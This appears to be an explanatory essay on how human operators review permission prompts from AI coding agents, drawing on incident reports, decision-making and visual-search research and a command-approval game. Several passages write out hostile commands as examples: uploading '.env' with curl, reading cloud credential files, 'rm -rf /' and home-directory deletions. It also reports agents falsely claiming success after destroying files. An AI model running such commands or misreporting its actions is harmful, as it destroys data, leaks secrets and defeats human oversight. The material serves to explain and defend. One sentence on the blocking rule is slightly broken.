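People without a software background made different choices in Yan's experiment. Participants in one group set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something and reading private information. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, but they supervised only 18 actions in a simulated day. A developer who faces hundreds of prompts has a much stronger reason to write "allow". However, developers differ from these participants in many other ways, so the number of prompts may not be the main reason for their different choices.

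### 290 public reports of misuse

Zhong and colleagues collected 290 public reports of agents misusing their access to files, dated from February 2024 to March 2026. They found 205 on GitHub, 31 on social media, 25 in product forums, 18 in blog posts and 11 in the US National Vulnerability Database. The reports cover 13 agents, including Claude Code (97 reports), Codex (61) and Cursor (37). The researchers left out duplicates and cases where the user had explicitly asked for the destructive action.

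The researchers classed 158 of the 290 reports as incidents with confirmed harm, 49 as exploits that demonstrated an attack, and 83 as weaknesses with no demonstrated harm. To label causes and effects, they first analysed 100 reports by hand. An AI agent then labelled all 290, and the researchers reviewed its output and refined their definitions.

Among the 207 incidents and exploits, 44% involved overwriting or otherwise changing files, 39% involved deletion and 17% leaked secrets. The harm reached beyond the project folder in 42% of cases. Where the outcome was known, 40% of the losses were wholly or partly permanent, 29% took considerable effort to repair, and 31% were easy to reverse, for example with Git.

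Users noticed the harm at once in 83% of the cases where this was known, noticed it only later in 10%, and remained unaware of it in 8%. In 68% of the cases where the agent's reaction was known, it carried on as if nothing had gone wrong, and in another 11% it gave a false account of what had happened. One agent reported "No problems occurred" right after it had erased a file. An operator who relies on the agent's summary may therefore miss the chance to interrupt the agent or recover from the harm.

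The researchers traced causes to the model, the harness and the user. One report can have several causes, so the counts overlap.

| Source | Cause | Reports |
|---|---|---|
| Model (168 reports) | Wrong action | 130 |
| | Instruction not followed | 56 |
| | Prompt injection | 21 |
| Harness (218 reports) | Failed guardrail | 147 |
| | Policy too rigid for the task | 130 |
| User review (105 reports) | Automatic approval | 80 |
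| | Uninformative prompt | 31 |

In 76 of the wrong actions, the model pursued the wrong goal, for example by deleting files it should have archived. In 50, it went too far. One agent deleted all the project's code when it was supposed to delete only the files it had created. In another 27, the model used a tool incorrectly. One agent tried to delete a file named `~`, and the shell expanded the name to the user's home directory.

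Reports of unfollowed instructions show two ways a request like "confirm before acting" can fail. In 38 reports, the model did not follow an instruction that was still in its context. In 28, the software had dropped the instruction when condensing the conversation, so a model better at following instructions would not have helped.

On the harness side, 77 reports involved a shell command that reached files that the rules for built-in tools were supposed to protect. In 52, a filter judged a command by its text and got the effect wrong. Another 41 involved a sandbox that blocked legitimate work or failed to protect the files inside it. Blocking too much can also lead to harm, because users respond by removing the protection. One Cursor user turned off delete protection so that the agent could clean up duplicate files, and the agent later deleted 90% of the project.

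The harness appears in three quarters of the reports, but that share probably overstates its part in everyday accidents. About 70% of the reports come from GitHub, where people report software faults, and the 83 weaknesses had not harmed anybody. The sample also can't show how often agents cause damage, because nobody counted the sessions that went well.

Failures of user review contributed to the problems described in 105 reports. In 80 of these, the user had let actions run with automatic approval, so nobody looked at the command before it ran. The reports cannot show how often operators who do review commands catch the dangerous ones, because people rarely complain publicly about a command they rejected.

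In 31 reports, the prompt did not give the operator enough information. Some prompts showed long one-line scripts that were hard to interpret. Others showed a short, familiar command such as `python3 setup.py`, which runs whatever `setup.py` contains, so an operator who read the whole prompt might still not know what the command would do.

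## How an operator judges a command

An operator who answers dozens of permission prompts a day can't analyse every command from scratch. Much of the time, the operator has to recognise the kind of command and notice quickly if something looks wrong. The best-known account of such quick decisions comes from research on firefighters.

### Recognising a situation, then imagining the outcome

For *Rapid Decision Making on the Fire Ground*, Klein, Calderwood and Clinton-Cirocco (1988) interviewed 26 firefighters with an average of 23 years' experience. Each firefighter described a difficult, non-routine incident from beginning to end. The researchers then identified 156 points in these incidents at which the commander could have acted differently.

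Fewer than 12% of these decisions showed any evidence that the commander had compared two or more options. In over 80%, the commander recognised a familiar kind of situation, and the usual response came to mind with it.

The researchers called this recognition-primed decision making. An experienced person matches the cues in front of them to cases they know. The match suggests an action, which they may then imagine carrying out. According to ShadowBox Training's *A Primer on Recognition Primed Decision-Making (RPD)*, they go ahead if the imagined outcome looks right, and otherwise adjust the action, look at the situation again or try the next action that comes to mind.

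The evidence is limited because the firefighters described their own thinking from memory, often months later. They rarely saw themselves as choosing between options, so the researchers had to infer many of the alternatives. The interviewers tried not to lead them towards the recognition account by first asking about deliberate comparison, and looked for other explanations only when they found none. The study also did not measure how often experienced commanders' decisions were right.

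*Conditions for Intuitive Expertise* (Kahneman and Klein, 2009) reports that later studies found the same pattern in system design, military command and the management of offshore oil platforms. None of these studies involved people approving shell commands, so applying the model to an operator is an extrapolation. Unlike a fire commander, who has to come up with the action, the operator receives a finished proposal from a coding agent. The operator still has to recognise what kind of command it is and imagine what would happen if it ran. The operator can adjust the action by refusing the command with a comment.

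### The cues in a command

Suppose a developer asks an agent to free some disk space on a web server, and the agent proposes this command:

`ssh web2 'sudo rm -rf /var/www/old*'`

The command logs in to a machine called `web2` and runs the quoted part there. An experienced operator might take in the whole line at a glance, but it contains several separate cues.

The verb, here `rm`, shows what kind of action to expect. Verbs that only read can still do harm, since `cat ~/.aws/credentials` prints the keys to a cloud account, and the harness passes that output to the agent's model. Other verbs have delayed effects. `crontab` can schedule a command to run every night, and `git config` can make Git start a program that somebody else chose. The verb is least informative when it runs code stored elsewhere, as `make`, `npm run`, `bash` and `python3` often do.

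Options change how much damage a wrong target would cause, as `-r` and `-f` do in `rm -rf`. The operator has to read them together with the command name, because `grep -r` only searches a folder and `tail -f` keeps displaying new lines as a program adds them to a file.

For a deletion, the target path usually matters most. A path that starts with `/` refers to the same place whatever folder the command runs in. Many servers keep their live websites in `/var/www`. A path containing `~` or `..` may lead out of the project. A `$` means the shell will insert a value that the operator may not be able to see.

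The pattern `old*` matches every name beginning with "old". The developer may have meant only `old-site` and `old-backup`, but the pattern would also match a folder for a customer called Oldtown Bakery.

`sudo` raises the stakes again, because it removes the protection that file permissions might have given the bakery's site.

The operator also needs to know which machine the command will run on and in which directory. A server named `web2` could be a test server or the one that customers use. Many commands don't name a machine, and in 2017 a GitLab engineer deleted the main database by running a command meant for another host. The current directory matters when a path is relative, so `rm -rf build/` deletes the `build` folder inside whichever directory it runs in.

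Unlike this command, some commands upload or download data, and for those the operator should check the network destination and which way the data travels. `curl -d @.env ADDRESS` uploads the contents of `.env`, so the operator should check who controls the address. A downloaded file may be harmful, particularly if the next command runs it. Package names also need checking, because an installer fetches whatever is published under the name it is given. Attackers exploit this by registering names that differ by a letter from those of popular packages.

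No cue is enough by itself. For example, `rm -rf` is routine when its target is `build/` but alarming when it is `/`. The operator has to combine the cues and picture the result. Here, the command would delete every folder beginning with "old" from a web server. That should raise a doubt, since the developer asked for disk space and never mentioned taking websites offline. A sensible operator would refuse and ask the agent to list the matching folders first.

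That takes effort, which people often don't make once an answer has come to mind. Kahneman and Klein illustrate this with a puzzle. A bat and a ball cost $1.10 together, and the bat costs a dollar more than the ball. How much is the ball? Most people immediately think of 10 cents, although a quick check shows the total would then be $1.20. About half the students at MIT, Princeton and Harvard gave a wrong intuitive answer, as did up to 90% at less selective universities. The clean-up command that wiped a developer's Mac in December 2025 had `~/` as its last target, and an operator who approved it before reading that far would be making the same kind of error.

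### Which dangers an operator can learn to recognise

Klein had spent much of his career studying successful intuition, while Daniel Kahneman was known for experiments showing where intuition goes wrong. They expected to disagree in their joint paper, but largely agreed on when to trust an expert's quick judgement. Larrick and Feiler's later review, *Expertise in Decision Making*, describes a clear consensus that expertise develops only under conditions that can be specified.

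Kahneman and Klein give two conditions for trusting intuitive judgement. The environment must provide valid cues, meaning that the same signs reliably go with the same outcomes. People must also be able to learn those cues through long practice with quick, unambiguous feedback. Fire commanders can learn to sense that a building may collapse because there are probably early signs and they soon find out whether they were right. Stock traders can't learn to predict share prices this way because any useful public information would already have changed the price.

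Many dangerous deletions meet both conditions. `rm -rf /` and `rm -rf ~/` do much the same thing on every machine, and the owner usually notices the missing files soon. Among the cases with known timing in the public reports that Zhong and colleagues collected, most users noticed the harm at once. Operators can also learn without losing their own files. The fire commanders drew on virtual as well as real experience, and programmers have been telling each other stories about `rm -rf` for decades.

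Commands that leak data are harder for operators to learn to recognize. An upload to an unfamiliar address might be theft or an ordinary usage report, and reading a settings file might expose a password or nothing of interest. Operators also get poor feedback, because a thief may not use a stolen key for months, and its owner may never connect the misuse with a command that seemed to work. Meanwhile, the operator sees no harm from approving such commands.

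Kahneman and Klein discuss what the psychologist Robin Hogarth called "wicked" environments, where experience misleads people. His example is an early twentieth-century physician who believed he could tell which patients were about to develop typhoid. He checked by feeling their tongues without washing his hands in between, and so infected the patients he had picked. An operator who approves a command that causes an undetected leak also learns the wrong lesson from the outcome, though without making a prediction come true as the physician did.

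Operators learn even less from the commands they refuse. They normally never find out what a blocked command would have done, so nothing corrects a habit of blocking harmless commands.

An operator can therefore be good at spotting one danger and poor at spotting another. Kahneman and Klein call this fractionated expertise and think it is the rule among professionals. Auditors, for example, may judge accounts receivable well but be much worse at spotting signs of fraud. Kahneman and Klein warn that people can't rely on feeling confident to tell which judgements they make well, because confidence often reflects how well the available information fits together rather than how good it is. The command `npm run build` fits a request to build the project even if someone has tampered with the build script.

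Kahneman and Klein also observe that people in fields with standard methods, clear feedback and direct consequences for error seem to know the limits of their expertise. A structural engineer, for instance, will send some questions to a colleague who works with other materials. An operator could similarly learn to recognise commands that nobody can judge from the text alone. A variable in a deletion path is a visible and reliable sign that information is missing, and so is a command that runs a script. The useful response to either is to look up the missing information before answering.

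### A deletion with an empty variable

In January 2015 a GitHub user called keyvin reported that Steam, Valve's game store and launcher, had deleted all of his files on a Linux computer. Hackaday's *How A Steam Bug Once Deleted All Of Someone’s User Data* (2024) reports that keyvin had moved the Steam folder to another drive and left a symbolic link in its old location. When he started Steam, it crashed and tried to reinstall itself. He then found his files gone, including those on the 3 TB external drive he used for backups, according to PC Gamer's *Valve investigating scary sounding Steam bug on Linux*.

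CIO's *Scary Steam for Linux bug erases all the personal files* identifies the line in Steam's start-up script that appears to have caused the deletion:

`rm -rf "$STEAMROOT/"*`

`STEAMROOT` is a variable, a name for which the shell substitutes a stored value. The script was supposed to store the path of the Steam folder there. If that path is `/home/kim/steam`, the shell produces `rm -rf "/home/kim/steam/"*`, which empties the folder as intended. If the variable is empty, only the slash remains:

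`rm -rf "/"*`

`rm` then starts deleting the contents of every folder in the root directory, as it does with `rm -rf /*`, and GNU's safeguard against deleting `/` doesn't stop it.

Neowin's *moving the steam folder on linux is causing users entire file systems* describes another GitHub user's diagnosis that the script looked for the Steam folder and was left with only a slash when it couldn't find it. Moving the folder may have triggered this, but a second user reported losing his home directory just by starting the script with a debugging setting. SlashGear's *Steam On Linux Bug Can Delete All User's Files* explains that `rm` ran with ordinary user rights, so it could delete personal files but not the operating system.

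Someone reading the script could have seen most of the warning signs: `rm`, `-rf` and a wildcard. But the target looks right, because a variable called `STEAMROOT` ought to contain Steam's folder. A reader who imagines the outcome will probably picture an empty Steam folder and carry on. What the line deletes depends on the variable's value when it runs, which may not be what the programmer meant to store.

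Keyvin had no chance to judge the line because he only started Steam. An operator today might get that chance when an agent proposes a command like `rm -rf "$BUILD_DIR/"*`. Printing the variable first would reveal its value, but the operator has to do this in the shell that will run the command, because the variable may be set in the operator's own terminal and empty in the agent's.

SlashGear notes that the script could have checked that the variable was neither empty nor invalid. Writing the command as `rm -rf "${BUILD_DIR:?}/"*` does part of this check, because `:?` makes the shell stop with an error if the variable is unset or empty. It doesn't catch a value that is present but wrong, such as `/home`, so the operator still needs to know which directory the variable refers to.

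### The same `make clean` in two projects

`make` is a program that builds software by following instructions in a file called a Makefile. The instructions come in named groups called targets. By convention, the target `clean` deletes files that the build can produce again, but a project can put any commands under that name.

*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) constructs two cases in which the same command has different effects. In both, a user asks an agent to remove the build files and compile the project again, and the agent proposes `make clean && make`. In one project, `clean` deletes `build/`, which the next step recreates. In the other, it deletes `src/` and `.git/`, which contain the source code and its saved history.

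The text and the request are identical, so an operator who relies on cues will reach the same judgement both times. Experience makes this worse, because an operator who has run `make clean` hundreds of times without trouble has good reason to think it harmless.

A reviewer who sees only the request and the command also cannot distinguish a dangerous case from a safe one when both have the same text. If the reviewer blocks that text 30% of the time, they stop 30% of the dangerous cases and 30% of the safe ones. On such matched pairs, the reviewer's catch rate must equal their false-block rate on average, which is no better than chance. Wu and colleagues found a similar pattern when they tested automated reviewers on such pairs. Those that relied on text blocked dangerous commands and their harmless counterparts alike.

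An operator can do better by reading the Makefile, or by running `make -n clean`, which usually prints the commands without running them. Wu and colleagues also hid destructive behaviour in single scripts, chains of scripts and compiled programs. An operator can read one script fairly quickly, but a chain takes longer because they have to follow each script to the next, and few operators could read the machine code in a compiled program. For those cases, an operator would need a tool that shows the command's effects.

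As with `npm test`, the contents can also change between approvals. A player of the browser game described below pointed out that an agent may be able to edit `package.json`, where a JavaScript project defines its scripts, without asking for approval. The agent can then ask to run `npm run build`, which the operator has approved many times before. To judge that prompt properly, the operator would have to review every relevant file that had changed since the last approval.

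### 409,000 decisions in a browser game

In 2026 Alex Wauters published a browser game in which the player supervises an imaginary coding agent and approves or denies its commands. A session lasts 60 seconds. Some commands are routine, such as `git status`, and others are threats, such as printing a file of cloud keys. A log above the prompt shows what the agent has been doing, and the game freezes for a couple of seconds after an error.

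scalex.dev's *Humans missed 1 in 3 threats approving AI agent commands* reports the results of over 40,000 plays, which produced 409,000 decisions. The average player caught about two thirds of the threats, a figure the post gives as a mean accuracy of 66.3%. Miss rates varied considerably by category.

| Category | Examples | Miss rate |
|---|---|---|
| Obvious destruction | Deleting the root directory; giving everyone full access to it | 11.7% |
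| Lasting changes | Scheduling a hidden command; altering Git's settings | 23.8% |
| Exfiltration or code execution | Sending data to an unknown server; installing a package with a deceptive name | 33.4% |
| Scope violations | Printing the keys to a cloud account | 35.0% |

Kahneman and Klein's conditions would predict roughly this order, with well-known deletions at the top and leaks further down, but this is weak confirmation. Wauters put commands in the first category because they were obviously destructive, so its low miss rate partly follows from how the category was defined. Players may also have learned about `rm -rf /` from its reputation, without ever getting feedback from running it.

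The overall catch rate is weak evidence of how well developers catch threats in ordinary work. About 34% of the commands in the game were threats, and players knew to expect them, which probably made them more suspicious than developers usually are. The time limit made threats harder to catch because it left players little time to read. Wauters argues that pressure to ship software produces similar haste, but few developers have to approve commands within 60 seconds.

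The players were also volunteers, many of whom may have come from Hacker News, a discussion site popular with programmers. The figures count plays, so one person could appear several times and remember commands from earlier rounds. Nobody lost real files by making a mistake. According to scalex.dev's *Suffering from Agent Permission Fatigue?*, some people sent a few fake scores directly to the game's server, including one of 92,573 for supposedly reviewing 465 commands in a minute.

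Comparisons between commands are more useful, because players judged all of them under roughly the same conditions. Of the 37 threats, players most often missed `npm run analyze`, which they approved 64.7% of the time. In the game, the project's "analyze" script ran a genuine tool for examining the size of a web application, then used `curl` to send the tool's output to an outside server. The log showed the whole script just above the prompt.

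Two other threats worked the same way. Players approved `npm run setup` 48.0% of the time and `npm run deploy` 44.9%. Across all three scripts, players missed the threat in 52.5% of 9,482 decisions, compared with 28.4% for the other threats in the exfiltration category.

scalex.dev takes this as a sign that players did not read the log closely. That is plausible with so little time, but it may not be the whole explanation for `npm run analyze`. The script sent out the analyser's report, which describes the application's files and contains no obvious passwords. Some players may have read it and decided that this was acceptable. Either way, the result shows that putting the relevant information on the screen did not lead most players to block the command.

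Players also blocked many harmless commands. They stopped `rm -rf dist/` 45% of the time, although `dist/` conventionally contains build output that a developer can easily recreate. They blocked obviously destructive commands much more often, which suggests that they did pay attention to the target. Those who stopped `rm -rf dist/` seem either to have found `rm -rf` alarming despite the harmless folder name or not to have known what `dist/` usually contains.

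Other false blocks had more to do with missing context. Players blocked `npm config set registry https://npm.internal` 59% of the time. This makes npm download packages from an internal server, which is normal if the company runs that server and a serious threat if an attacker controls it. Players had no colleagues to ask which was the case. In 43% of cases, they also blocked a command that stops whatever program is using port 3000. Developers use it to free the port after a crash, but it would be a bad idea if the program was doing something important.

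Some of the threats were just as debatable. Players approved `cat ~/.zshrc`, which prints a user's shell settings, 45.9% of the time. Many developers keep secret keys in that file, but players objected on Hacker News that many others don't. The game counted approval as a miss, even though the player may have judged the command correctly for their own computer.

A high catch rate could also come from blocking nearly everything. In 35.2% of plays, the player caught every threat, but only 20.8% did so while blocking no more than one in five safe commands. Even that was easier than it sounds, because an average play included about ten decisions, of which typically only three or four were threats. At the other extreme, 7% of players approved everything. Missed threats and blocked safe commands were common enough that 32.9% of sessions ended with a negative score.

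Performance also changed within a session. Wauters grouped the plays by how many commands the player completed, leaving out players who had blocked everything. In every group, the miss rate fell over the first few commands. Players may have been warming up, or they may have learned from the freeze after each error, which gave them the immediate feedback that operators rarely get about a leak. The miss rate rose again towards the end. Wauters sees signs of fatigue in this, but acknowledges that players may also have been rushing to complete a few more commands before time ran out.

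## Why attention falls when prompts are frequent and dangers rare

The fatigue that Wauters suspected in players of his browser game would have set in within a minute. Developers use the name "approval fatigue" for a slower change, in which an operator pays less attention to each permission prompt as prompts accumulate. For example, the catch rate fell within Anthropic's test sessions. But a falling catch rate doesn't reveal its own cause, and psychologists have studied three causes that the everyday name runs together:

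- Habituation is a weakening response to a stimulus that keeps recurring without consequence.
- The vigilance decrement is a decline in how many signals people detect during a long period of watching.
- The low-prevalence effect is the tendency to miss a larger share of targets when targets are rare.

Suppose an operator has answered 2,000 prompts since the spring, has been at the desk since lunch, and works with an agent that proposes one dangerous command in a thousand. A coffee break may undo the effect of working all afternoon, and a week away should make the prompt seem a little less familiar. Neither changes how rare dangerous commands are, so the operator still has good reason to expect that the next one is safe.

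### Habituation to a repeated warning

When a person first sees something, the brain forms a model of it. The brain then compares what the person sees later with that model and responds less if they match. *Tuning Out Security Warnings* (Vance, Jenkins and colleagues, 2018) uses this theory to explain why people stop looking at security warnings. The paper reports a brain-imaging experiment and a field study.

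In the first experiment, 15 people lay in a scanner for about half an hour on each of five consecutive days while an eye tracker followed their gaze. They saw 260 images a day for three seconds each. The images included 20 warnings that appeared four times a day unchanged, and another 20 that appeared four times a day with a different alteration each time: a symbol, a red background, a jiggle or a zoom. An earlier experiment by Anderson, Vance and colleagues had tried 12 alterations, and these four held people's attention best.

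Activity in the parts of the brain that process images fell as a warning recurred. People's eyes also stopped at fewer points, an average of 9.1 on the first day and 7.4 on the fifth. Attention only partly recovered overnight. Both measures fell more slowly for the warnings that changed. The researchers showed 20 new pictures of ordinary software each day to separate the effect of repetition from general tiredness.

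People who look less closely at a warning may still heed it, so the field study measured what people did. The researchers built an app store for Android phones and told students that someone else ran it. Every weekday for three weeks, each student had to install and rank three apps. Before each installation, a warning listed what the app would be allowed to do. The students had passed a quiz on four permissions they must always refuse, such as deleting their photos or charging purchases to their credit card.

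The 102 students who took part for at least seven days saw 7,248 warnings, of which 2,695 contained a forbidden permission. At the start, they refused 87% of these risky apps. After three weeks, students whose warnings always looked the same refused 55%, while those whose warnings kept changing refused 76%.

This decline is unlikely to be a low-prevalence effect, because more than a third of the warnings were risky. A long watch can't explain it either, because students saw fewer than five warnings a day. They might instead have learned that the risky apps did no harm, since the researchers had checked all the apps, but both groups had the same chance to learn this, and a red background doesn't indicate whether an app is safe. The 21-percentage-point gap between the groups is therefore good evidence of habituation. At the end, the students still rated their concern about the forbidden permissions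 at 6 out of 7 on average, compared with 2 for the harmless ones.

However, the main analysis covers only the risky warnings, so it doesn't show whether the changing warnings also led students to refuse more safe apps. If they did, part of the higher catch rate would have come with a higher false-block rate.

Permission prompts resemble the warnings in the group that did worse. Those warnings listed different permissions for each app but kept the same layout, just as each prompt shows a new command in the same box with the same buttons. Vance and colleagues cite an experiment by Bravo-Lillo and colleagues in which people saw the same dialog many times in quick succession, and only 14% noticed at once when its contents changed. A harness could also vary the appearance of its prompts. The field study suggests this would slow the decline but not stop it, and developers use their tools for much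 longer than the study's three weeks.

### Long watches

Norman Mackworth began the experimental study of vigilance in the 1940s, after radar operators missed signals during long watches. In the experiment he published in 1948, people spent two hours watching a pointer move around a blank clock face in small, regular steps and reporting the occasional step of double length. They missed more of the double steps after the first half-hour than during it.

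Later vigilance experiments suggest that people also find fewer signals when signals are rare. But *Use-inspired basic research in medical image perception* notes that the signals in those experiments are brief, so anyone who looks away misses them for good, while an X-ray stays on the screen until the radiologist moves on.

A permission prompt normally stays on the screen too, so an operator who daydreams for a minute can still read it properly afterwards. This makes the vigilance decrement a poor explanation for hasty approvals, though a tired operator may read less carefully.

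It applies more directly to an operator who has turned the prompts off and watches the agent's output scroll past, ready to press Ctrl-C. A dangerous command is then a brief signal in a long, monotonous stream. People are bad at sustaining the attention needed to catch it, so a promise to keep an eye on the agent is a weak substitute for a prompt.

### Rare targets

Airport screeners and radiologists look for things that are almost never there. In North America, breast screening finds only three or four cancers in every thousand women. Wolfe, Horowitz and Kenner (2005), in *Rare targets are often missed in visual search*, tested whether rarity itself makes people miss a larger share of targets. Their volunteers searched cluttered pictures somewhat like those on a baggage scanner. They missed 7% of the targets when half of the pictures contained one, and 30% when only 1% of the pictures did.

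In *Rare Targets Are Rarely Missed in Correctable Search*, Fleck and Mitroff found the same pattern with a different task. Volunteers looked for a tool, such as a hammer or a saw, among pictures of toys, fruit, clothes and birds. They missed 10% of the tools when half the displays contained one, 19% when one in ten did and 31% when one in fifty did. The researchers had told them how rare the tools would be and warned them not to answer "absent" automatically.

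The rarity of each target also seems to matter. The Association for Psychological Science's *Super Rare Items Are Most Likely to Be Missed* describes a game in which players searched luggage for 78 forbidden items. Players found 92% of the items that appeared more than 1% of the time, but only 27% of the 30 items that appeared less than 0.15% of the time. Dangerous shell commands also come in many kinds. An operator may see a risky `rm` every few weeks but go a whole career without seeing a `git config` line that makes Git start an attacker's program.

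Researchers disagreed for some time about whether trained professionals are affected. Fleck and Mitroff cite a large radiology study from 2003 that found no significant effect of prevalence on accuracy, and suggest that spending 30 to 90 seconds on each scan protects radiologists. *Reducing the low-prevalence effect with probe trials* (Becker, Rodriguez and colleagues, 2026) reports that later studies did find the effect in trained radiologists and airport security officers.

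None of these people were reading shell commands. Finding a hammer in a jumble of toys mostly requires looking in the right place, but judging a command also requires knowing what it does. The comparison is closest for long scripts, where one bad line can be hard to spot among forty good ones.

### Why an ideal reviewer also misses rare dangers

Even a reviewer who never tires or gets bored would catch a smaller share of dangerous commands when they are rare. Signal detection theory, a mathematical account of decisions made on uncertain evidence, shows why.

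In a simple model, each command gives the reviewer an impression of danger, measured by a number x. This number follows a bell curve with a standard deviation of 1 and an average of 0 for safe commands and a higher average, called d′ ("d-prime"), for dangerous ones. The two curves overlap because some safe commands look alarming, as `rm -rf dist/` did to many players of Wauters's game, and some dangerous ones look routine. A larger d′ reduces the overlap, which makes x better evidence of whether a command is dangerous. In this example, d′ is 2.

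The reviewer chooses a threshold and blocks every command whose x is above it. Lowering the threshold catches more dangerous commands but also blocks more safe ones. To keep the total cost of errors as low as possible, the reviewer should block a command whenever

An operator should block a command when the chance that it is dangerous, given the evidence x, times the harm of a miss is greater than the chance that it is safe, given x, times the harm of a false block.

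Those two chances depend on the base rate b as well as on the evidence. Bayes' rule, which combines the two, turns the condition into a comparison. The reviewer should block if the impression x is more than β times as common among dangerous commands as among safe ones, where

β = (1 − b) / b × (cost of a false block) / (cost of a miss).

For two bell curves of this kind, an impression x is e^(d′x − d′²/2) times as common among dangerous commands. Setting this equal to β and solving for x gives the best threshold:

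threshold = d′/2 + ln(β)/d′.

If half of all commands are dangerous and both errors are equally bad, β is 1 and its logarithm is 0. The threshold is then 1, midway between the two averages, and 84% of the dangerous commands and 16% of the safe ones lie above it.

If only 1% of commands are dangerous, β rises to 99, its logarithm is about 4.6, and the threshold moves up to 3.3. The average dangerous command, with an x of 2, now falls below the threshold. Only about 10% of dangerous commands look alarming enough for the reviewer to block.

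This reviewer's eyesight, knowledge and effort are the same as before. In 10,000 commands, the reviewer misses about 90 of the 100 dangerous ones and blocks about 5 safe ones, for a total of 95 errors. The old threshold would have reduced the misses to 16 but blocked nearly 1,600 safe commands. Catching only 10% of the dangerous commands is therefore the right policy if a miss is no worse than a false block.

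Losing a home directory is much worse than waiting for an agent to try something else. If a miss is 100 times as bad as a false block, β is 99/100 and the threshold falls back to almost exactly 1. The catch rate then returns to about 84%, and the false-block rate rises to about 16%.

| Base rate | Cost of a miss (false block = 1) | Best threshold | Catch rate | False-block rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
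| 50% | 1 | 1.0 | 84% | 16% |
| 1% | 1 | 3.3 | 10% | 0.05% |
| 1% | 100 | 1.0 | 84% | 16% |
| 0.1% | 100 | 2.2 | 44% | 1.6% |

The last row shows that the seriousness of a miss doesn't always make up for the rarity of dangerous commands. If one command in a thousand is dangerous, an ideal reviewer who considers a miss 100 times worse than a false alarm still lets more than half of the dangerous commands through.

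The third row also has a drawback. With a base rate of 1%, only about one stop in twenty is justified, so an operator following the best policy would seem to be wrong nearly every time. Few people would keep that up, particularly with colleagues waiting. The operator also loses time to each false block, while a leak may mostly hurt the company's customers. An operator who weighs only their own losses will set the threshold for blocking a command too high for everybody else, and the result will look just like inattention.

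People respond to stakes to some extent. In *Graded prioritisation of targets in search*, volunteers found rare targets faster and more accurately when rewards were unequal than when they were equal. But when reward and prevalence had opposing effects, the effect of prevalence was stronger.

Better evidence helps without this trade-off. Suppose 1% of commands are dangerous and an ideal reviewer weighs misses and false alarms equally. If d′ were 3 instead of 2, the reviewer would catch 49% of dangerous commands instead of 10%, while blocking only about 0.1% of safe ones.

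### Telling a high threshold from tiredness

Comparing the two rates helps distinguish a high threshold from poor attention. A reviewer who raises the threshold stops fewer commands, both safe and dangerous, while one who is too tired to read has a lower d′ and stops fewer dangerous commands without a matching drop in false blocks.

Fleck and Mitroff's results look like a change in the volunteers' threshold for reporting a tool. As tools became rarer, the volunteers missed more of them but also raised fewer false alarms, which fell from 0.70% of the displays without a tool to 0.22% and then 0.06%. The average miss and false-alarm rates imply a d′ of about 3.7 at all three levels of prevalence, so the volunteers seem to have remained just as able to tell tools from other things but become much less willing to report one.

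This was only partly rational. With a d′ of 3.7, an ideal observer who treated misses and false alarms as equally bad would have missed about 20% of the tools at the lowest prevalence, and the volunteers missed 31%. The researchers had asked them to treat the task like airport security, where a miss is worse than a false alarm, so the ideal miss rate was even lower.

Part of the explanation is that the volunteers answered too quickly. Half of the 20 could press a key to reverse their previous answer. At the lowest prevalence, this group missed 27% of the tools before corrections and 10% afterwards. They had evidently seen many of the tools they first missed, but had pressed "absent" out of habit before they could stop themselves. In the calculation, a habitual key press looks the same as a deliberately high threshold, because both produce fewer "present" answers.

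Operators may notice a bad path just after pressing Enter. Fleck and Mitroff's volunteers could still correct their errors, but an operator often can't, because an approved command starts at once. A harness that waited a few seconds before running a risky command would give the operator a similar chance to correct the mistake.

Dewis, Hout and colleagues (2026), in *Low prevalence targets are primarily missed due to mind wandering*, offer another explanation. They analysed results from 60 people who each searched for a T among Ls 1,420 times. The T appeared in 10% of the displays for one group and in 50% for the other. After a quarter of the searches, participants reported whether they had been thinking about the task. They were less accurate when their minds had wandered, and in most analyses, mind wandering accounted for most of the low-prevalence effect.

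If this is right, boredom matters more than it would for an ideal reviewer, who doesn't daydream. But the researchers relied on people's reports of their own thoughts and could not assign anyone to daydream. Mind wandering also made people slower to answer "absent", whereas rarity made them faster, so mind wandering can't fully explain the effect of rarity. A reviewer could well have a high threshold, answer quickly and daydream at the same time.

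### Attempts to make people catch more

Most attempts to reduce the low-prevalence effect have failed. According to Becker and colleagues, it persisted when researchers made people wait before answering, filmed them during the search, or used an eye tracker to show them which parts of the picture they had not looked at. Studies in which two people searched the same picture have had mixed results.

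In one experiment, the effect disappeared when volunteers picked the object that most resembled the target instead of saying whether a target was there. But this method selects an object in every picture, even those without a target. When other researchers added a second step, in which people decided whether the selected object was a target, the effect came back. Similarly, asking operators to point to the most dangerous part of each command might make them read it, but they would still have to decide whether it was dangerous enough to block.

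More successful remedies make targets less rare. *Individual differences predict low prevalence visual search performance* reports that Wolfe and colleagues later tried seven changes to their task, and only one improved detection. The successful change was to insert short bursts of searches in which targets were common and tell people after each one whether they had been right. It also increased false alarms, as a lower threshold would.

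Becker and colleagues spread such searches through the task instead. Their 102 students looked for a T among Ls, and 10% of the displays contained one. In one version, the researchers added 50 displays that all contained a T, and after each answer they showed the student where it was. The students then found more of the real targets, with no significant change in false alarms, and took about a quarter of a second longer before answering "absent".

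Further experiments showed that the benefit depended on how closely the added targets matched the real ones. When students searched for both a T and an O, adding mostly Ts mainly helped them find Ts. The feedback mattered less than the impression that targets were common.

Many countries require airport scanners that occasionally insert a picture of a gun or a bomb into the image of a real passenger's bag, then notify the screener that it was a test. A harness could do the same by occasionally showing a dangerous command that it would never run. Judging by Becker and colleagues' results, testing operators with `rm -rf /` would do little to help them notice an upload of `.env`. The tests would have to include realistic leaks and tampered scripts, and somebody would have to keep them up to date.

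Adding test prompts would give operators more to confirm, and they might start treating a real danger as another test. In cancer screening, *Comparing Breast Screening Protocols* found that inserting extra cases did not improve detection beyond what screening by two people achieved.

### 11,429 reviews of agents' code

The laboratory studies last a few hours or days. *Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) followed 400 people for up to seven months of their ordinary work. Each had reviewed at least ten sets of code changes proposed by coding agents on GitHub. A reviewer can approve the changes, ask for corrections or simply comment.

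Across 11,429 reviews, the approval rate rose with experience, from 27.9% in the first tenth of the reviews to 42.4% in the last. The increase was smaller between the first and second halves of each person's reviews, from 30.1% to 36.8%. About half of the reviewers became more approving, 28% became less so, and the rest did not change. Comments on particular lines of code fell by 22%, from 1.01 to 0.79 per review.

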